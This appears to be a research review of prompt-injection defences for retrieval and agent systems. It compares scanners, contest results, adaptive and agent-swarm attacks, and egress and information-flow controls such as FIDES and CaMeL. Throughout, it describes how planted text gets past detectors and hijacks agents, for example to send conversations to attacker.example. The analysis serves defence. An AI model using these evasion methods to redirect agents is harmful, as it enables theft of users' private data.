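An attacker could also use quarantine to make information unavailable. *LLM Safeguard is a Double-Edged Sword* (2024) describes attacks that exploit a filter's false alarms to block legitimate requests, and the same idea could work against a document collection. If customers can comment on the shop's returns page, an attacker could post a comment that contains a typical attack phrase. The scanner would be right to flag the comment, but if the whole chunk were withheld, the assistant would lose access to the returns policy.

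Keeping comments and page text in separate chunks prevents the simplest version. The shop could also alert staff when a scanner flags part of a page they had approved, and quickly restore the approved version. *SearchInject* recommends tracking false quarantines by source, because the average can be low even when one publisher's pages are repeatedly quarantined by mistake.

If the operator retrains the scanner on reviewed flags, attackers can gain another way to attack it. *Rapid Poison* (2026) describes attacks on detectors that are trained on newly reported attacks and extra examples generated by a language model. An attacker who injects instructions into that process can teach the detector to flag innocent text that has a harmless feature, such as a particular name or document format. The attacker can also teach it to miss real attacks that contain a chosen topic. An operator can reduce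 this risk by having people check new training examples and by testing each retrained scanner on a fixed set of the company's own harmless documents before using it.

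## How many attacks do scanners catch, and do they hold against attackers who adapt?

The best scanners flag more than 99% of attacks in some tests, but attackers who can keep rewording their text still get past them. This is possible because recall, the share of attacks a scanner catches, is measured over a set of texts, most of which were not written with that scanner in mind. An adaptive attacker, who knows or probes the defence and changes the attack to suit it, needs only one text that the scanner misses.

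### A contest with 461,640 attempts

*LLMail-Inject* (Abdelnabi, Fay and colleagues, 2025) describes a public contest that tested scanners inside a complete retrieval system. Between December 2024 and April 2025, 839 people made 461,640 attempts to hijack a simulated email assistant, each by writing an email to the assistant's user. An attempt succeeded only if the email reached the assistant's model, no scanner flagged it, and the model then sent a message with the right recipient and content.

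The contest had four levels. At the first two, the user asked for a summary of the latest two or ten emails, which always included the attacker's. At level 3, the user asked about a project, and the attacker's email had to rank among the ten most relevant. At level 4, which added data theft, the user asked about the second-quarter budget, and the attack had to make the assistant send the attacker a profit forecast from another email.

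The assistant ran on either GPT-4o-mini or Microsoft's Phi-3-medium. At each level, contestants faced one of five defences: Microsoft's text classifier Prompt Shield, the activation probe TaskTracker, a language-model judge, spotlighting, or all four together. The organisers set each scanner to flag less than 5% of harmless text. Contestants knew which defence they faced and could retry without penalty. After each attempt, they learned which steps had worked but never saw the assistant's answer.

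The first phase ended in February 2025 after about 371,000 attempts. The table shows how many got through each step.

| Step | Attempts remaining |
|---|---|
| Contestant submitted an email | 371,000 |
| Email reached the model's context | 362,000 |
| No scanner flagged it | 180,000 |
| Model called the email tool | 7,200 |
| Recipient was correct | 6,100 |
| Content was also correct | 3,000 |

Fewer than 1% of attempts succeeded. The organisers also recorded how the model responded to the 183,000 emails that scanners flagged. It called the tool for 34,000 of them, or 19%, compared with 4% of the unflagged emails. In 21,400 of those 34,000 calls, both the recipient and the content were correct. So the scanners stopped about 88% of the 24,400 emails that would otherwise have completed the attack.

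The gap between 19% and 4% probably does partly reflect a trade-off between evading a scanner and hijacking the model, as the organisers believe, but the comparison exaggerates the effect. Some unflagged emails were harmless text that contestants sent to see how the defences behaved. The unflagged group also includes every attempt against spotlighting alone, which doesn't flag anything. With longer contexts, almost no attack on Phi-3 worked under spotlighting, perhaps because the model couldn't read the marked text properly.

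### How the defences compared

To measure recall, the organisers reran every scanner on the 25,323 different emails from phase 1 that had made a model call the tool. They also counted false alarms on 1,000 real emails from the Enron archive. The table combines these results with the contest's own. The level 4 figures are for GPT-4o-mini, and the number of attempts is an average across all levels.

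| Defence | Recall (%) | Teams that beat it at level 4 (%) | Attempts before first success | Harmless emails flagged (%) |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Text classifier | 60–68 | 60 | 89 | 0.0 |
| Spotlighting | – | 53 | – | – |
| TaskTracker | 76–95 | 44 | 159 | 4.0–5.7 |
| Language-model judge | 99.4 | 32 | 506 | 5.0 |
| All together | 99.8 | 17 | – | 10.0 |

The text classifier was the weakest, and the organisers suggest it couldn't distinguish attacks from the requests in ordinary work emails. EchoLeak got past a deployed classifier in the same way.

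Lowering the classifier's threshold may not be an easy improvement, even though the classifier raised no false alarms on the Enron emails. *Confidently Wrong* (Biswas, 2026) tested three other classifiers, one from ProtectAI and two versions of Meta's Prompt Guard 2, on several kinds of attack. The share of attacks they missed ranged from 1% to 97%, but in every case they gave the missed attacks an average probability of at most 1% of being an attack. A threshold low enough to catch those attacks would probably also flag much harmless text.

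The judge was the best single defence, but it flagged one harmless email in 20. All the defences together flagged one in ten, which the organisers consider too many for real use without further tuning. At that rate, a company with a million chunks would lose access to about 100,000 harmless ones.

The average number of attempts leaves out teams that never succeeded, so it understates how hard the judge was to beat. The number of attempts also varied widely between teams.

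### Why 99.4% recall still let a third of teams through

Recall counts emails, whereas the level 4 figure counts teams, and each team could send hundreds of emails. Suppose a fraction h of a team's emails would hijack the assistant if nothing blocked them, and the scanner misses a fraction m of those. If the attempts are independent, the chance of at least one success in n attempts is

1 − (1 − h × m)ⁿ

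The judge's recall of 99.4% means that it misses 0.6% of attacks (m = 0.006). If one email in ten would work without a scanner (h = 0.1), each attempt has a 0.06% chance of success. A team then has about a 6% chance of at least one success after 100 attempts, 26% after 500, and 70% after 2,000. The value of h is an assumption, but the example shows that a success rate of 32% among teams is unsurprising.

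Real attempts aren't independent, because teams learn from their failures. Many of the 25,323 emails also came from teams trying to beat some other defence, so the judge's recall would probably be lower on emails written specifically to fool it.

A scanner's miss rate can also overstate how often attacks succeed. *PIDS-Bench* (2026), a set of tests for detectors, counts an attack as successful if the detector fails to flag it, whatever the model does next. By that standard, all 180,000 unflagged emails in phase 1 would have been successes, although only 3,000 completed the attack.

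### The second phase and newer models

The organisers ran a second phase in March and April 2025, with 218 new participants and 90,916 attempts. They updated the classifier and TaskTracker, rewrote the judge's instructions, added warnings and delimiters to every defence, and blocked phase 1 attacks and close paraphrases of them. Nobody beat the full set of defences on GPT-4o-mini, but a screenshot of the leaderboard shows three teams had beaten it on Phi-3.

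This is the strongest result for scanners in the contest, but phase 2 used only the first two levels, so the improved defences were never tested on the data theft task. The organisers also made all their changes at once, so they can't tell which one helped. The attacks seem to have become harder to detect, since the classifiers' recall fell to 43–49% on phase 2 emails and the judge's fell to 96.5%, though TaskTracker's rose to 90–99.8%, depending on the model it used.

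The organisers later replayed contest emails on models that hadn't been in the contest, counting any unauthorised call to the email tool as a success. The emails worked on GPT-4o in 58% of cases, on GPT-5 mini in 47%, on Meta SecAlign in 32% and on GPT-5 in 22.8%. Meta had trained SecAlign specifically to resist injection, and attacks had succeeded against it less than 5% of the time on older benchmarks. GPT-5's attack success rate on the standard agent benchmarks had been at most 0.2%. Those benchmarks repeat a few fixed attack templates, so a low rate on them is weak evidence that a model will resist attacks written by inventive people.

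More recent models did better against new attacks. GPT-5.4 wrote 500 attack emails based on a list of the contestants' strategies and did not revise the ones that failed. The emails worked 18% of the time on GPT-5.4-mini and 2% of the time on GPT-5.2.

### Current models as scanners

In *BrowseSafe++*, Chen, Zhang and colleagues (2026) tested current models as scanners on web pages. They built 38,675 pairs of pages that differed only in whether an injection was present, and most of the injections came from real websites. The recall figures in the table are calculated from the published accuracy, given that half of the test pages were clean.

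| Scanner | Page format | Recall (%) | Clean pages flagged (%) |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-6 Astra | HTML | 97 | 14.3 |
| GPT-5.5 | HTML | 98 | 21.0 |
| Claude Opus 5.5 | HTML | 80 | 4.0 |
| BrowseSafe-Guard | HTML | 98 | 1.4 |
| BrowseSafe-Guard | Markdown | 94 | 7.4 |

BrowseSafe-Guard, the researchers' own detector, has only 0.8 billion parameters, but it was trained on other pairs from the same collection, which gives it an advantage over the general models. Its results on Markdown, a simple text format, are more relevant to a RAG system that converts pages to text before splitting them.

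Without tuning, the general models still raise too many false alarms to scan a whole company's documents. But even a capable assistant can benefit from a separate scan. Chen and colleagues found that some models recognised an injection when asked to look for one, yet followed the same injection while working on a user's task.

### The Attacker Moves Second

In *The Attacker Moves Second* (October 2025), Nasr, Carlini and colleagues from OpenAI, Anthropic, Google DeepMind and several other institutions reported attacks on 12 published defences. Some of the defences were meant to stop prompt injection and others to stop jailbreaks, in which users themselves try to make a model break its rules. The researchers argue that developers had tested these defences against fixed lists of attacks or weak automated ones, which shows little about how well they work against an attacker who studies the defence.

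Nasr and colleagues tested defences with automated searches that revised the attack text after each result, and with a contest of more than 500 participants. The attack success rates originally reported for most of the defences were near zero, but the new attacks succeeded more than 90% of the time against most of them. Munirathinam cites an earlier test in which attacks bypassed eight defences against indirect injection, each more than half the time.

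These rates are the share of test cases in which the search eventually found a working attack, not the share of individual attempts that worked. Nasr and colleagues assumed an attacker with ample computing power because they were testing whether each defence could be broken at all, not how much effort it would take. In the tests of standalone detectors, the automated attacker also received the detector's score and verdict after each attempt, which few real attackers would see.

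*Defending against Adaptive Prompt Injection Attacks via Reasoning-enabled Task Alignment* (He, Wang and colleagues, 2026) tested several of the same defences against attackers who saw only how the agent behaved. The table gives attack success rates in percent. That paper's figures are averages over several attack methods on the small model Qwen3-4B.

| Defence | Nasr and colleagues, adaptive | He and colleagues, fixed | He and colleagues, adaptive |
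|---|---|---|---|
| None | – | 33.3 | 32.1 |
| ProtectAI's classifier | over 90 | – | – |
| PromptGuard | over 90 | 10.3 | 27.9 |
| Google's Model Armor | over 90 | – | – |
| PIGuard | 71 | 3.3 | 33.8 |
| DataSentinel | every case | 23.4 | 27.9 |
| MELON | 76–95 | 3.9 | 20.8 |
| Spotlighting | over 95 | 29.1 | 28.3 |

PIGuard is another trained classifier. MELON runs the agent a second time with a harmless task in place of the user's request and flags tool calls that occur in both runs. MELON's higher figure is for an attacker who knew exactly how it worked.

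He and colleagues report much lower rates, but their results support the same conclusion about most scanners. PIGuard cut the success rate of fixed attacks from 33.3% to 3.3%, but adaptive attacks succeeded about as often with it as with no defence. MELON did better, reducing the success rate of fixed attacks by 88% and of adaptive attacks by 35%. The adaptive tests used only 40 cases, which He and colleagues chose because the undefended model was vulnerable to them, so small differences between the adaptive results mean little.

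The results are more encouraging for the defence that He and colleagues built themselves. They trained the agent to check whether each planned action follows from the user's task, instead of looking for signs of an attack. Adaptive attacks succeeded in 2.9% of cases on average, and in 7.5% with the most effective method. However, only the team itself attacked the defence in these tests, and many of the defences that Nasr and colleagues broke had similar figures beforehand.

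People were still better than machines at finding attacks in 2025. On a selected set of test cases, the automated search succeeded 69% of the time, while the human contestants together found an attack for every case. The contestants also produced 123 successful injections against the strictest detector setting.

Nasr and colleagues call detectors "useful—but limited". They think detectors are worth using because they are easy to add and stop unsophisticated attacks. This fits the email contest results, where scanners stopped most of the emails that would otherwise have worked but rarely stopped every team.

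### Attacks by teams of AI agents

By late 2026, AI agents could do much of the work that had recently required human ingenuity. *Scaling Adaptive Prompt Injection Attacks with Agent Swarms* (Kurakin, Karande and colleagues, November 2026) reports Google DeepMind's tests of attacks by 16 cooperating agents. The agents worked in pairs, shared notes and could see one another's best attempts. Each agent could query the target model 20 times per test case, for a total of 320 queries.

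The researchers used 100 simulated tasks. An attack succeeded if text in a tool result made the model call an unrelated tool with the right inputs, such as one that records a blood pressure reading when the user was booking a tutor. The table gives the percentage of cases in which the model resisted every attempt by agents running on Gemini 4 Argon, the strongest attacker.

| Model under attack | Within 150 queries | Within 320 queries |
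|---|---|---|
| Gemini 4 Argon | 87 | 66 |
| Gemini 3.8 Flash | 34 | 10 |
| Gemini 3.7 Flash | 31 | 6 |
| Gemini 3.6 Flash | 3 | 1 |
| Kimi K3 | 5 | 1 |
| GLM-5.3 | 1 | 1 |
| DeepSeek V4.1 Flash | 1 | 1 |

The attacker's ability mattered a great deal. Gemini 4 Argon resisted every attack within 150 queries when the attacking agents ran on the weaker Gemini Flash models. As models improve, they can therefore get better at both resisting and writing injections. The number of attempts matters too. The 2.0% success rate for Claude Opus 5 in the first section came from only 15 attempts, so it can't show how the model would do against hundreds.

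The researchers switched off Gemini's external injection defences, so these tests measured how well the models resist on their own. They also chose harmless goals so that a model couldn't pass by recognising a dangerous request. A model that records an irrelevant blood pressure reading might still refuse to send a conversation to a stranger, so the failure rates probably overstate the risk of data theft.

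In a smaller test, Kurakin and colleagues left Gemini 3.6 Flash's external defences on and used the older AgentDojo tasks. Attack agents running on GLM-5.3 succeeded in 6 of 80 cases within 25 queries, compared with 2 of 80 for an existing open-source attack. Gemini failed at a much higher rate in the main test, but that test had a larger budget and different tasks. The external defences may have helped, but we can't tell from this test by how much.

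### Can detection ever be enough?

Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian (2026), in *AI Agents May Always Fall for Prompt Injections*, argue that weak scanners are only part of the problem, because whether an agent should act on a message depends on facts about the situation, such as who sent it and what the user has authorised. For example, an email might ask for a travel refund and mention that the department head has approved it. The agent should process the refund if the approval is genuine but not if an attacker invented it, and the wording can be identical in both cases.

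Their proof makes this precise. Suppose the agent has no way to tell the two cases apart. It must then act with the same probability, p, in both. Its chance of carrying out the attack is p, and its chance of refusing the genuine request is 1 − p, so

P(carries out the attack) + P(refuses the genuine request) = p + (1 − p) = 1

An agent that obeys such an attack only 10% of the time will therefore also refuse 90% of the genuine requests that look the same. A scanner has the same limitation if it must judge both messages from the same information.

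Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian say the proof doesn't show that such indistinguishable cases exist in every system. An agent that can look up the approval in the company's records can tell the two cases apart. But they expect unverifiable claims to become more common as agents do more on their own, and argue that attackers can invent claims faster than developers can add checks.

The argument is stronger for refunds than for data theft. The kitchenware shop has little reason to send a customer's conversation to an address it has never used, so refusing every such request would block few genuine ones. Refusing helps less when the stolen data goes into a report or an email to a known contact, because an assistant has many good reasons to write those.

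Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian also tested two versions of Prompt Guard on 8,400 realistic work emails. Half claimed that someone had already authorised the assistant to reply, and the other half only invited a reply. The scanners' AUC was 0.43 and 0.59, where 0.5 is no better than guessing. The test was hard because the scanners received only the email, while the right action depended on the user's instructions. A scanner that also receives the user's request, as Rai's does, might do better.

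The Decoder's *OpenAI admits prompt injection may never be fully solved* concludes that using agents for banking or confidential documents is hard to justify without a fundamental fix. That conclusion would follow if detection were an agent's only protection. Defenders of scanning can also point out that scanners make attacks weaker and harder to carry out, and that real attackers have fewer advantages than researchers.

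### Does evading a scanner weaken the attack?

Rewording an instruction to get past a scanner may also make the model less likely to follow it. Biswas measured this with a program that rewrote attacks to evade the scanners. The original attacks succeeded 38.5% of the time and the rewritten ones 15.4–19.8%, so rewriting cut the success rate roughly in half. This is better evidence than the 19% and 4% from the email contest, because it compares attacks before and after rewriting.

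A quick rewrite weakens an attack, but an attacker with enough time and feedback can recover most of its lost effectiveness. Nasr and colleagues searched for text that could both get past the detector and hijack the model, and they succeeded in more than 90% of cases against three of the four standalone detectors.

### Does stacking scanners help?

Munirathinam argues that combining scanners that work in different ways is more useful than improving any one scanner, because the attacker has to evade all of them with the same text. The email contest supports this. At level 4, 17% of teams beat the combined defences, while 32% beat the judge alone.

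The benefit was smaller than it would be if the scanners made unrelated mistakes. In the replay of phase 1 emails, one text classifier missed 39.6% of the attacks, two versions of TaskTracker missed 23.9% and 11.9%, and the judge missed 0.6%. If these misses were independent, all four would miss

0.396 × 0.239 × 0.119 × 0.006 ≈ 0.00007

of the attacks, or about 2 of the 25,323. They actually missed 0.2%, or about 50. Some emails were evidently hard for every kind of scanner, and those are the ones an adaptive attacker looks for.

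Nasr and colleagues found that their attacks still got past several detectors combined, and they conclude that stacking detectors doesn't solve the underlying problem. Their attackers had much more feedback and computing power than the contestants, so this result and the contest's can both be right. Stacking probably stops more attackers who have limited time, but it doesn't stop a well-equipped one. It also doubles false alarms from 5% to 10% in the contest's setup.

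### Do real attackers get enough feedback?

Most attackers can't see a company's scanner or its scores. Someone who plants a document in a private corpus usually learns that the attack worked only if data arrives at the webhook. If nothing arrives, they don't know whether the retriever, the scanner or the model stopped it.

The real-world injections that Chen and colleagues collected succeeded on only a few percent of tasks as written. After a program revised them using the agents' responses, they succeeded on an average of 78.8% of tasks.

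An attacker who gets no feedback can still make many attempts. *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* (2026) reports that several common strategies each succeeded in 3.4% of attempts in a large public competition. At that rate, an attacker who made 20 independent attempts would have an even chance of succeeding at least once.

A skilled attacker may not need many attempts either. In another test, Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian used Claude Sonnet 4.6 to attack an email assistant running on the same model. The user had asked the assistant only to read emails, and the attack succeeded if it sent one. Emails from their earlier dataset succeeded in 0.67% of 150 scenarios, while those that the attacking model wrote and revised succeeded in 96.7%. The attacking model's first email, written before it received any feedback, worked in 61.4% of cases. However, the attacking model had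 the assistant's system instructions, which an outsider would usually have to guess.

The best emails also worked on other models without further changes, so an attacker can develop an email on one model and use it against another. They succeeded in 92.6% of cases against Gemini 3 Pro, 89.3% against GPT-5.2 and 63.3% against GPT-5.4. However, these tests used no scanner, and the assistant only had to send an unauthorised email, not private data.

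How much feedback an attacker gets also depends on who can use the assistant. An attacker could pose as a customer of the kitchenware shop and ask for a refund after each change to the planted page, but couldn't easily test an assistant that only employees can use. Repeated attempts would also leave evidence. Teams that beat the judge in the email contest needed about 506 attempts on average before their first success, and a reseller who uploaded even 20 flagged pages would stand out in the shop's quarantine log. Attackers can avoid leaving this evidence by practising elsewhere, but that prepares them for the shop's scanner only if they can get a copy of it. Anyone can get a copy of an openly available scanner such as Prompt Guard.

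## What stops the data leaving when a scanner misses?

Even the best scanners miss some attacks, so an operator should assume that the model will sometimes read and follow a planted instruction. In *L3M*, Eisenach, George and colleagues (2026) build agent software at Amazon on this assumption. Only a person's earlier decisions determine what their software lets the model do, even if text the model reads changes what it tries to do.

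Suppose the kitchenware shop's assistant has written a web request that would post a customer's conversation to attacker.example. Software outside the model can still refuse the request because of its destination, ask a person to approve it, or trace the data and the decision back to their sources. The shop could also have kept the planted page away from any model that can make web requests. Each of these defences makes the agent somewhat less useful, and the strictest can block more than half of its legitimate tasks.

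### Rules on where data may go

An egress control is a rule about where data may go, enforced outside the model. The most common kind is an allow-list. In L3M, a person lists the hosts an agent may contact, and the software checks every web address against that list before making a request. The shop's list would contain only couriers' websites, so the software would block the request to attacker.example however persuasive the planted page was.

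An allow-list fails if an approved domain passes data on, as a Microsoft Teams service did in EchoLeak, or if it lets the attacker collect data there, for example through public posts. The shop can reduce this risk by replacing its general web tool with a parcel-tracking tool that accepts only a tracking number and builds the web address itself, so the model has nowhere to put the conversation.

Removing unnecessary tools helps too. In *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025) tested a defence in which GPT-4o discards the tools it won't need before starting a task. On the AgentDojo benchmark, this cut successful attacks from 152 to 20. The defence can't stop an attack that uses a tool the task needs.

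Limits on an agent's tools don't cover images and link previews, so the chat page has to block outside images, and messaging services need previews turned off. Users lose some pictures and previews, and they can still leak data by clicking a link.

A defence has to block the request carrying the data before it leaves. *WebMCP-Phalanx* (Lee, Chang and colleagues, 2026) describes a browser system that monitors image loads and other outgoing requests from tools that web pages offer to agents. If a supposedly read-only tool makes such a request, the system lowers the tool's trust rating. This can prevent a second leak, but the first request may already have left.

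### Asking the user

A confirmation message is useful only if it shows the destination and the data, as in "Send your name, email address and messages to attacker.example?" A customer who sees only "Allow web request?" has almost no basis for objecting. Even with the full details, a customer can't know which outside companies the shop uses to keep its records.

People also approve requests out of habit. Costa and colleagues warn that frequent prompts cause confirmation fatigue and leave users open to social engineering. Lee and colleagues therefore ask users only about the least trusted tools.

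L3M puts a second model between the agent and the person to review any risky call. This reviewer may suggest a safer way to do the same work. The software asks a person only if the two models still disagree, and it refuses by default if nobody is there to answer. Eisenach and colleagues acknowledge that the agent's stated reason can leave out where a value came from or what private data a request contains. The software should therefore take the destination and data in the message directly from the call.

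### Labels that follow the data

Information-flow control bases the decision on where data came from and who may see it. It works in three steps:

1. The software labels each piece of data with its origin, trusted or untrusted, and with the people allowed to read it.
2. Whenever the system combines data, the result gets the strictest labels of its parts. One untrusted part makes the whole result untrusted, and only people allowed to read every part may read the result.
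3. Before each tool call, the software checks the labels against fixed rules.

The table shows how this could work in the shop.

| Data | Origin | Who may read it |
|---|---|---|
| Customer's messages | Trusted | Customer, shop |
| Order record | Trusted | Customer, shop, courier |
| Shop's returns page | Trusted | Anyone |
| Reseller's "Refund policy" page | Untrusted | Anyone |
| Whole context | Untrusted | Customer, shop |

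Costa and colleagues at Microsoft give two basic rules. An agent may take an action with consequences only in a trusted context, and it may send data only to recipients on that data's list of permitted readers. The request to attacker.example breaks both rules, but so does a legitimate parcel check, because the reseller's page has made the context untrusted and the courier isn't permitted to read the customer's messages.

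FIDES, the researchers' system, reduces this problem by storing untrusted text in a variable. Only the variable's name enters the main model's context, so that context stays trusted, and the model can pass the contents to a tool without reading them. The contents keep their own labels. If the shop's software stored the tracking number this way too, the assistant could send it to the courier without exposing the customer's messages. When a task requires reading the untrusted text, FIDES gives it to a separate model that has no tools and stores that model's output in a variable too.

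None of the AgentDojo attacks achieved a real injection against FIDES with the rules switched on. The table shows the percentage of user tasks that GPT-4o completed when there was no attack.

| Tasks | Ordinary agent, no rules | Ordinary agent, with rules | FIDES, with rules |
|---|---|---|---|
| Office work | 75.0 | 37.0 | 59.0 |
| Travel | 70.0 | 73.0 | 41.0 |
| Banking | 98.8 | 37.5 | 52.5 |
| Slack | 93.3 | 20.0 | 47.6 |

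FIDES regained much of the performance lost to the rules in three of the four areas. In travel, many tasks used tools that the rules allowed even in an untrusted context, so hiding the text only made the work harder. FIDES's travel score rose to 68% with OpenAI's o1, a stronger model at the time.

The guarantee depends on correct labels. Labelling was easy in the test because Costa and colleagues marked a field as untrusted if any attack in the benchmark used it, but the shop would have to work out for itself which fields an attacker could write to. FIDES treats the user's messages as public by default. Unless the operator changes that setting, only the rule about trusted contexts will protect conversations.

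The rules stop the agent from copying secret data directly, but its behaviour can still hint at that data. For example, if the agent checked parcels only for expensive orders, someone who saw its requests could learn which orders were expensive. The standard version of the software checks tool calls but not answers to the user, so it could miss a leak through an image in an answer. Costa and colleagues note that the software can check answers as well.

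### Planning before reading

CaMeL, a 2025 system from Google DeepMind and ETH Zurich, makes the agent plan before it reads anything untrusted. One model sees the user's request and writes a short program that includes every tool call the task may need. A second model, which has no tools, processes the untrusted text. For the broken kettle, the program might be:

```
order  = get_order(4417)
pages  = search_corpus("refund for a broken kettle")
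answer = reader_model("Answer the refund question", pages, order)
reply(answer)
```

The planted page can distort the answer, but it can't add a web request to the program, because the first model wrote the program before the search. The software that runs the program also labels the data and checks its rules at each tool call. *CaMeLoT* (2026) explains that these rules can block some unsafe actions even if an attacker has corrupted the plan. The shop would still need its rule against outside images, because the second model could write an image address into the answer.

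In *The LLMbda Calculus*, Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026) reran CaMeL on AgentDojo's 16 banking tasks, three times each, with GPT-5.2. With its rules on, CaMeL blocked the attack in all 231 runs that finished, but it completed only 18 of 48 harmless runs (37.5%), compared with 32 (66.7%) with the rules off. Even without the rules, separating the plan from the untrusted text stopped 239 of 240 attacks. The rules therefore added very little protection in this test, partly because two-thirds of the combinations of task and attack required a tool call that the plan would never contain.

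Garby and colleagues also found two gaps in how CaMeL tracks secrets. CaMeL relabels a variable only when the program changes it, so a variable that stays the same because a bank balance is high can reveal that the balance is high while still labeled public. A program that restarts after every refusal can leak a secret one yes-or-no answer at a time. An attacker who plants a document can't write the program, so they would probably have difficulty exploiting either gap.

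The paper's own agent, Randori, regained the lost tasks by using a plan that specifies in advance which untrusted data the agent may act on. It completed 75% of harmless runs with GPT-5.2, and attacks succeeded in 2 of 1,296 runs across three models. In both successful attacks, the user had asked the agent to pay a bill by following the instructions in a file, and the attacker had replaced the file. Labels can't distinguish the genuine bill from the false one if the user has authorised the agent to follow whatever the file contains.

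Stronger models lose fewer tasks when they have to plan before reading any data. In *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026) ran CaMeL without its rules on a set of industrial maintenance tasks. It lowered the completion rate by an average of 21.6 percentage points across five models, but by 13.4 points for the two strongest, Claude Fable 5 and GPT-5.5. The rules may still block as many tasks for stronger models, because a rule that forbids a necessary step stops every model. In the banking test, GPT-5.2 and MiMo-v2.5 each completed 18 runs with the rules on.

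CaMeL can also fail when agents work in teams. Peters-Gill and colleagues planted an instruction in a database of job applicants and asked a coordinating agent to send a summary to a colleague on Slack. The coordinator never read the database entry, but the software inserted the entry's text into the coordinator's request to a messaging agent. Every agent was running CaMeL, but the messaging agent treated the whole request as its user's instructions and emailed the applicants' details to the attacker.

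The researchers propose sending instructions and untrusted data between agents through separate channels. Across five models and 949 attack cases per model, attacks succeeded 12.9% of the time without CaMeL, 0.2% with separate CaMeL agents and 0.0% with the new channels. GPT-5.5 resisted every attack without these protections, so the benchmark is too easy to show how much a current model would gain from them.

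### Checking each call against its sources

Agent-Sentry lets the agent plan freely and checks each proposed action against records of earlier, legitimate work. Sequeira, Iqbal and colleagues (2026), in *Agent-Sentry*, describe three checks:

1. A classifier examines the sequence of tool calls and the source of each input, then allows the call, blocks it or marks it as uncertain. It doesn't interpret the wording of retrieved text, so rephrasing an attack shouldn't affect it.
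2. For uncertain calls, the software looks up sensitive inputs, such as account numbers and email recipients, in a list of values from past harmless runs. It allows the call only if they are on the list and come from trusted sources.
3. A language model judges any remaining calls by comparing them with the user's request.

Agent-Sentry's list can distinguish cases that an ordinary allow-list can't. In one test, some users wanted to email a colleague, Lily, while an attacker also tried to send her a message. An ordinary allow-list has to permit or forbid her address in every case. Agent-Sentry can detect that the address came from retrieved text and that the user hadn't asked to email anyone.

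The second check doesn't cover web addresses because they change too often. If the classifier's result for the request to attacker.example were uncertain, the judge would therefore make the decision.

The table compares Agent-Sentry with CaMeL and with Progent, which limits tool calls through written policies. Sequeira and colleagues created the new set, a large collection of runs. The older sets are AgentDojo and a similar benchmark, AgentDyn. All figures are percentages except the time per run.

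| System | Attacks blocked, new set | Attacks blocked, older sets | Harmless runs allowed, new set | Harmless runs allowed, older sets | Seconds |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Agent-Sentry, trained classifier | 96.8 | 91.2 | 96.4 | 69.1 | 4.3 |
| Agent-Sentry, simple rules | 95.3 | 93.2 | 89.3 | 87.1 | 5.5 |
| Progent | 97.7 | 88.4 | 69.2 | 93.7 | 4.3 |
| CaMeL | – | 99.3 | – | 31.0 | 26.6 |

The figures in the table come from runs that weren't used to fit Agent-Sentry. The paper's headline result is better, with 94.3% of attacks blocked and 95.1% of harmless runs allowed, but the researchers fitted and tested that version on the same runs. The comparison with CaMeL is also uneven, because Agent-Sentry only had to approve recordings of tasks that an agent had already completed, while CaMeL had to complete the tasks itself.

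Agent-Sentry relies on the agent's model to report the source of each input, although the attacker may have hijacked that model. The software checks some of these reports against the retrieved text, which reduces the risk but doesn't remove it. Like the standard version of FIDES, Agent-Sentry doesn't inspect answers, so it wouldn't stop a leak through an image.

The judge can also approve a harmful action that fits the request. *AgentAntibody* (Weng, Feng and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of a user who tells an agent to handle requests for a report. Sending the report to an outsider who asks for it follows that instruction, but the user would probably want to approve it first. The paper's system learns such limits from the user's corrections. The share of attacks that had succeeded fell from 35.0% after five attacks to 6.1% after 80, so an attacker has the best chance before the system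 has learned much.

### A reader with no tools

A separate model can also read the untrusted page and pass only a narrow answer to the agent. FIDES and CaMeL both use such a reader, and its answer can be as short as one word.

In an L3M example, an agent needs to know whether a public web page reports a fault in some software. A small program gives the page to a new model that has no files, network access or other permissions. The program accepts only "yes", "no" or "unclear", and converts any other reply, failure or timeout to "unclear". It passes the answer to the agent, which never sees the page.

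A choice among n answers carries at most log₂(n) bits of information, so a choice among three carries at most about 1.58 bits per call, or about 15.8 bits over ten calls. This limit assumes that the timing of the answers reveals nothing. A hijacked reader can still give the wrong answer, but it can only move the agent between three paths chosen in advance. If none of those paths sends the conversation outside, the planted page can't make the agent send it.

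The kitchenware shop could use this method to ask whether a page allows refunds for damaged goods. It couldn't ask for a summary of the page, because a summary is free text, which could contain a new instruction. Eisenach and colleagues present the method as a design and don't report how many attacks it stops or how many tasks it can handle.

The same idea can limit how much data leaves. In another L3M design, one agent has the private files but no network access, and a second agent searches the web without seeing the files. If the first agent sends a single message of k bytes, padded to a fixed length, and has no other way to reach the second, at most 8k bits of private information can get out. That limit can still be too high, since a 200-byte message has room for a customer's name, email address and last four card digits. L3M also doesn't yet enforce such a limit.

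Yu, Xing and colleagues (2026), in *Cordon-MAS*, apply the isolated reader to RAG, using short factual claims instead of fixed answers. One model reads the retrieved documents and turns them into claims, for example that a certain herb supports sleep. An auditor then scores each claim:

R = I × (1 − S)

The auditor scores each claim as I × (1 − S), where I measures how much the answer changes without the claim and S is the share of comparable claims from other documents that agree with it. It rejects claims that score above 0.65. For example, an influential claim with little support, with I = 0.9 and S = 0.1, scores 0.81 and is rejected. If S were 0.5, the score would be 0.45 and the claim would pass. Another model checks whether the accepted claims are enough to answer the question, and a final model writes the answer without seeing the documents.

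On five public question sets, planted falsehoods succeeded 2.1% of the time, compared with 27.5% in an ordinary RAG system. On one set of scientific claims, the rate was 2.0% in one sample and 26.5% in another. When several planted documents supported one another, 63.3% of attacks got through the whole system.

Cordon-MAS answered only 60% of clean questions and refused the rest. When it did answer, it was correct more often than ordinary RAG, so it correctly answered about 49% of all questions, compared with 53% for ordinary RAG. It took 2.2 times as long and cost 2.8 times as much.

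Yu and colleagues tested attacks that cause false answers, but didn't test attacks that steal conversations. The reader would probably drop the shop's planted instruction because it isn't a fact about refunds. But a claim can contain a short sentence, which gives an attacker much more room than L3M's three words.

### What the guarantees cost

Unlike scanners, some of these defences set limits that don't depend on an attack's wording, provided that the operator has configured them correctly.

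| Defence | Firm limit on the attacker | Extra cost | Usefulness lost |
|---|---|---|---|
| Scanner | None | From milliseconds to a model call per chunk | Some harmless chunks |
| Address allow-list | No direct requests to unlisted hosts | Very little | Access to new sites |
| FIDES | No direct copying of data to forbidden recipients | More complex tasks and extra model calls | 16–46 percentage points of GPT-4o's completed tasks |
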